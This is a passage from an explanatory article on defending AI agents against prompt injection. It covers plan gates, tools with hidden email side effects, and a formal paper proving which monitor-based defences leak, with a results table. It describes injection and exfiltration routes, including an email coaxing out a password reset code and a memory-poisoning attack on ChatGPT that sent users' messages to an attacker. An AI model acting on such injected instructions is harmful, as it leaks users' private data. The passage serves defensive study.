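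Kurakin and colleagues cite a more destructive combination. Listing files, encrypting them and deleting the originals are routine tasks in separate sessions, but together they can amount to a ransomware attack.

To prevent such combinations, the gate needs a record of earlier plans, and rules that check new plans against it. For salaries, it could block an average for any group that differs by fewer than five people from a group already averaged. This rule would still miss some combinations of three or more averages. A reviewer who reads the whole week's log might notice the pattern, which can't be seen from Tuesday's plan alone.

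A tool may also do more than its contract states. Suppose the contract for `create_event` lists only a new entry in Michelle's calendar, but the calendar service also emails each entry to everyone invited. A plan could then send a mailbox summary to an outside guest by putting it in the event's description. The gate would accept the plan, and a stronger rule about email wouldn't help, because the gate has no record that `create_event` sends email.

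To find such effects, the operator can run each tool in an isolated environment, record its network requests and file changes, and compare them with the tool's contract. The operator should repeat this after every update. Here, it is more useful for a person to review the tool before installation than for Michelle to review each plan, because the plan doesn't show the hidden email.

### Machine-checked definitions of security

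*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, November 2026) gives formal definitions of security against prompt injection and proves results about several kinds of defence. Claude models helped write the proofs, and Isabelle/HOL, a program that checks every step of a proof, verified them.

In the main model, a trusted planner sets the plan before the agent reads anything untrusted. While the plan runs, the language model may follow an instruction in an email and insert an extra tool call. A runtime monitor allows or denies each call. The language model has more freedom here than in Meijer's design, where only the interpreter makes calls.

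Dongol defines security by comparing the real agent with a reference agent, which runs the same plan under the same monitor but never obeys untrusted content. The real agent is "relatively secure" if an injection lets an attacker tell two private values apart only when the attacker could also do so by sending something to the reference agent. A stricter definition, requiring that nothing an attacker receives depends on private data, would reject useful agents, such as an assistant that sends Alice's calendar to anyone who asks her for a meeting.

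If an email tricks the assistant into sending Alice's calendar, that is not a new leak under the definition, because a genuine meeting request would also have obtained the calendar. If the email makes the assistant send a password reset code, the assistant is not relatively secure, because the reference agent never sends that code.

The main theorem is that every plan is relatively secure if the monitor withdraws every tool an injection could call as soon as the agent reads untrusted content, and never gives those tools back. The theorem assumes that each injection makes a single call, and that when the model obeys an injection doesn't depend on private data or the monitor's responses. It also assumes that the attacker sees the contents and order of messages but not their timing. The proof compares only runs in which the attacker receives the same number of messages between reads, so it doesn't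 rule out leaks through the number of calls. For agents that run indefinitely, the theorem also requires that the model can't keep obeying injections forever.

This protection can prevent an agent from finishing its task. For example, an agent can't reply to an email it has read if the monitor has withdrawn the sending tool. Because the reference agent has the same monitor, the definition doesn't account for this loss, and even a monitor that denies every call satisfies it.

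Dongol also proves results for 25 small example agents, including these:

| Defence | Result |
|---|---|
| Withdraw the sending tool before the first untrusted read | Secure against every single-call injection |
| Withdraw it after that read | Leaks |
| Allow one message, which the plan sends before reading | Secure against injected messages |
| Allow one message, which the plan sends after reading | Leaks, because an injected message can go first |
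| Have the user approve the next message, whatever it contains | Leaks |
| Have the user approve the exact message | Secure for contents and order, but leaks through timing |
| Mark untrusted text and tell the model not to obey it | Leaks unless the model respects the marking |
| Let only a model without tools read untrusted text | Leaks if the plan sends that model's answer |
| Also label private data and refuse to send it | Secure, but also blocks the honest reply |
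| Use the same labels in a plan that branches on the answer | Leaks through the choice of branch |

The last three rows are closest to Meijer's design, and their labels serve the same purpose as taint analysis. Each of these results applies to one plan, not to every plan with that defence. Some of the other secure results cover only the injections in the example. For example, one monitor allows web requests only to a newsletter, and Dongol proves it secure against two injected emails. A different email could make the agent request the newsletter only if a secret is 0, and an attacker who sees whether the request went out would learn something about the secret.

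An agent can also become insecure when an operator adds a tool. One of the example agents is secure with only the inbox or only the web-fetching tool, but it leaks with both. The operator should therefore repeat the tests whenever the set of tools changes.

The theorems apply to a real system only if it meets seven assumptions. A trusted interpreter must run the plan. The model must reach tools and untrusted sources only through the monitor, and untrusted content must not reach the model until the monitor allows the read. The attacker must not see refused calls or the system's internal steps, and must not be able to write to the sources the plan treats as trusted. A new session must clear everything the model has retained from untrusted content.

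Ordinary features can break these assumptions. Displaying a reply may load an image from an attacker's server, and a calendar that accepts invitations from outsiders isn't a trusted source. Dongol also models a reported attack on ChatGPT in which a web page planted an instruction in the system's long-term memory. In later conversations, the system loaded the instruction and sent the user's messages to the attacker.

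The definition covers only leaks, so it misses an injection that deletes Alice's files without revealing anything. It also ignores how much a single message reveals. Suppose an agent tells anyone whether a guessed PIN is correct. For any two PINs, an attacker could send the reference agent a guess that distinguishes them, so an injection that reveals the whole PIN at once still counts as relatively secure. Dongol gives a stricter definition that rejects this injection.

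The main limitation for Meijer's gate is that the definition treats the plan as correct. If a poisoned tool description makes the planner add a step that emails Eve, the reference agent emails her too, and the real agent passes. Dongol's theorems therefore can't replace a check of the plan, but they can extend its result to the real agent. If that agent is relatively secure, any limit on what the reference agent discloses also applies to it. A gate could prove such a limit from the plan alone, and the limit would then hold even when the model obeys an injection.

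Dongol's proofs of leaks also suggest a test. Each proof gives two private values and a single attacker input, and what the attacker sees depends on which value is used. An operator can prepare two test mailboxes that differ in one fact, put the same malicious email in both, and run the same plan on each. If the content or timing of the messages an outsider receives differs between the two runs, the operator should find out why and whether the user's request called for the difference. Because this test uses the real tools, it can also expose effects that the tools' contracts leave out.
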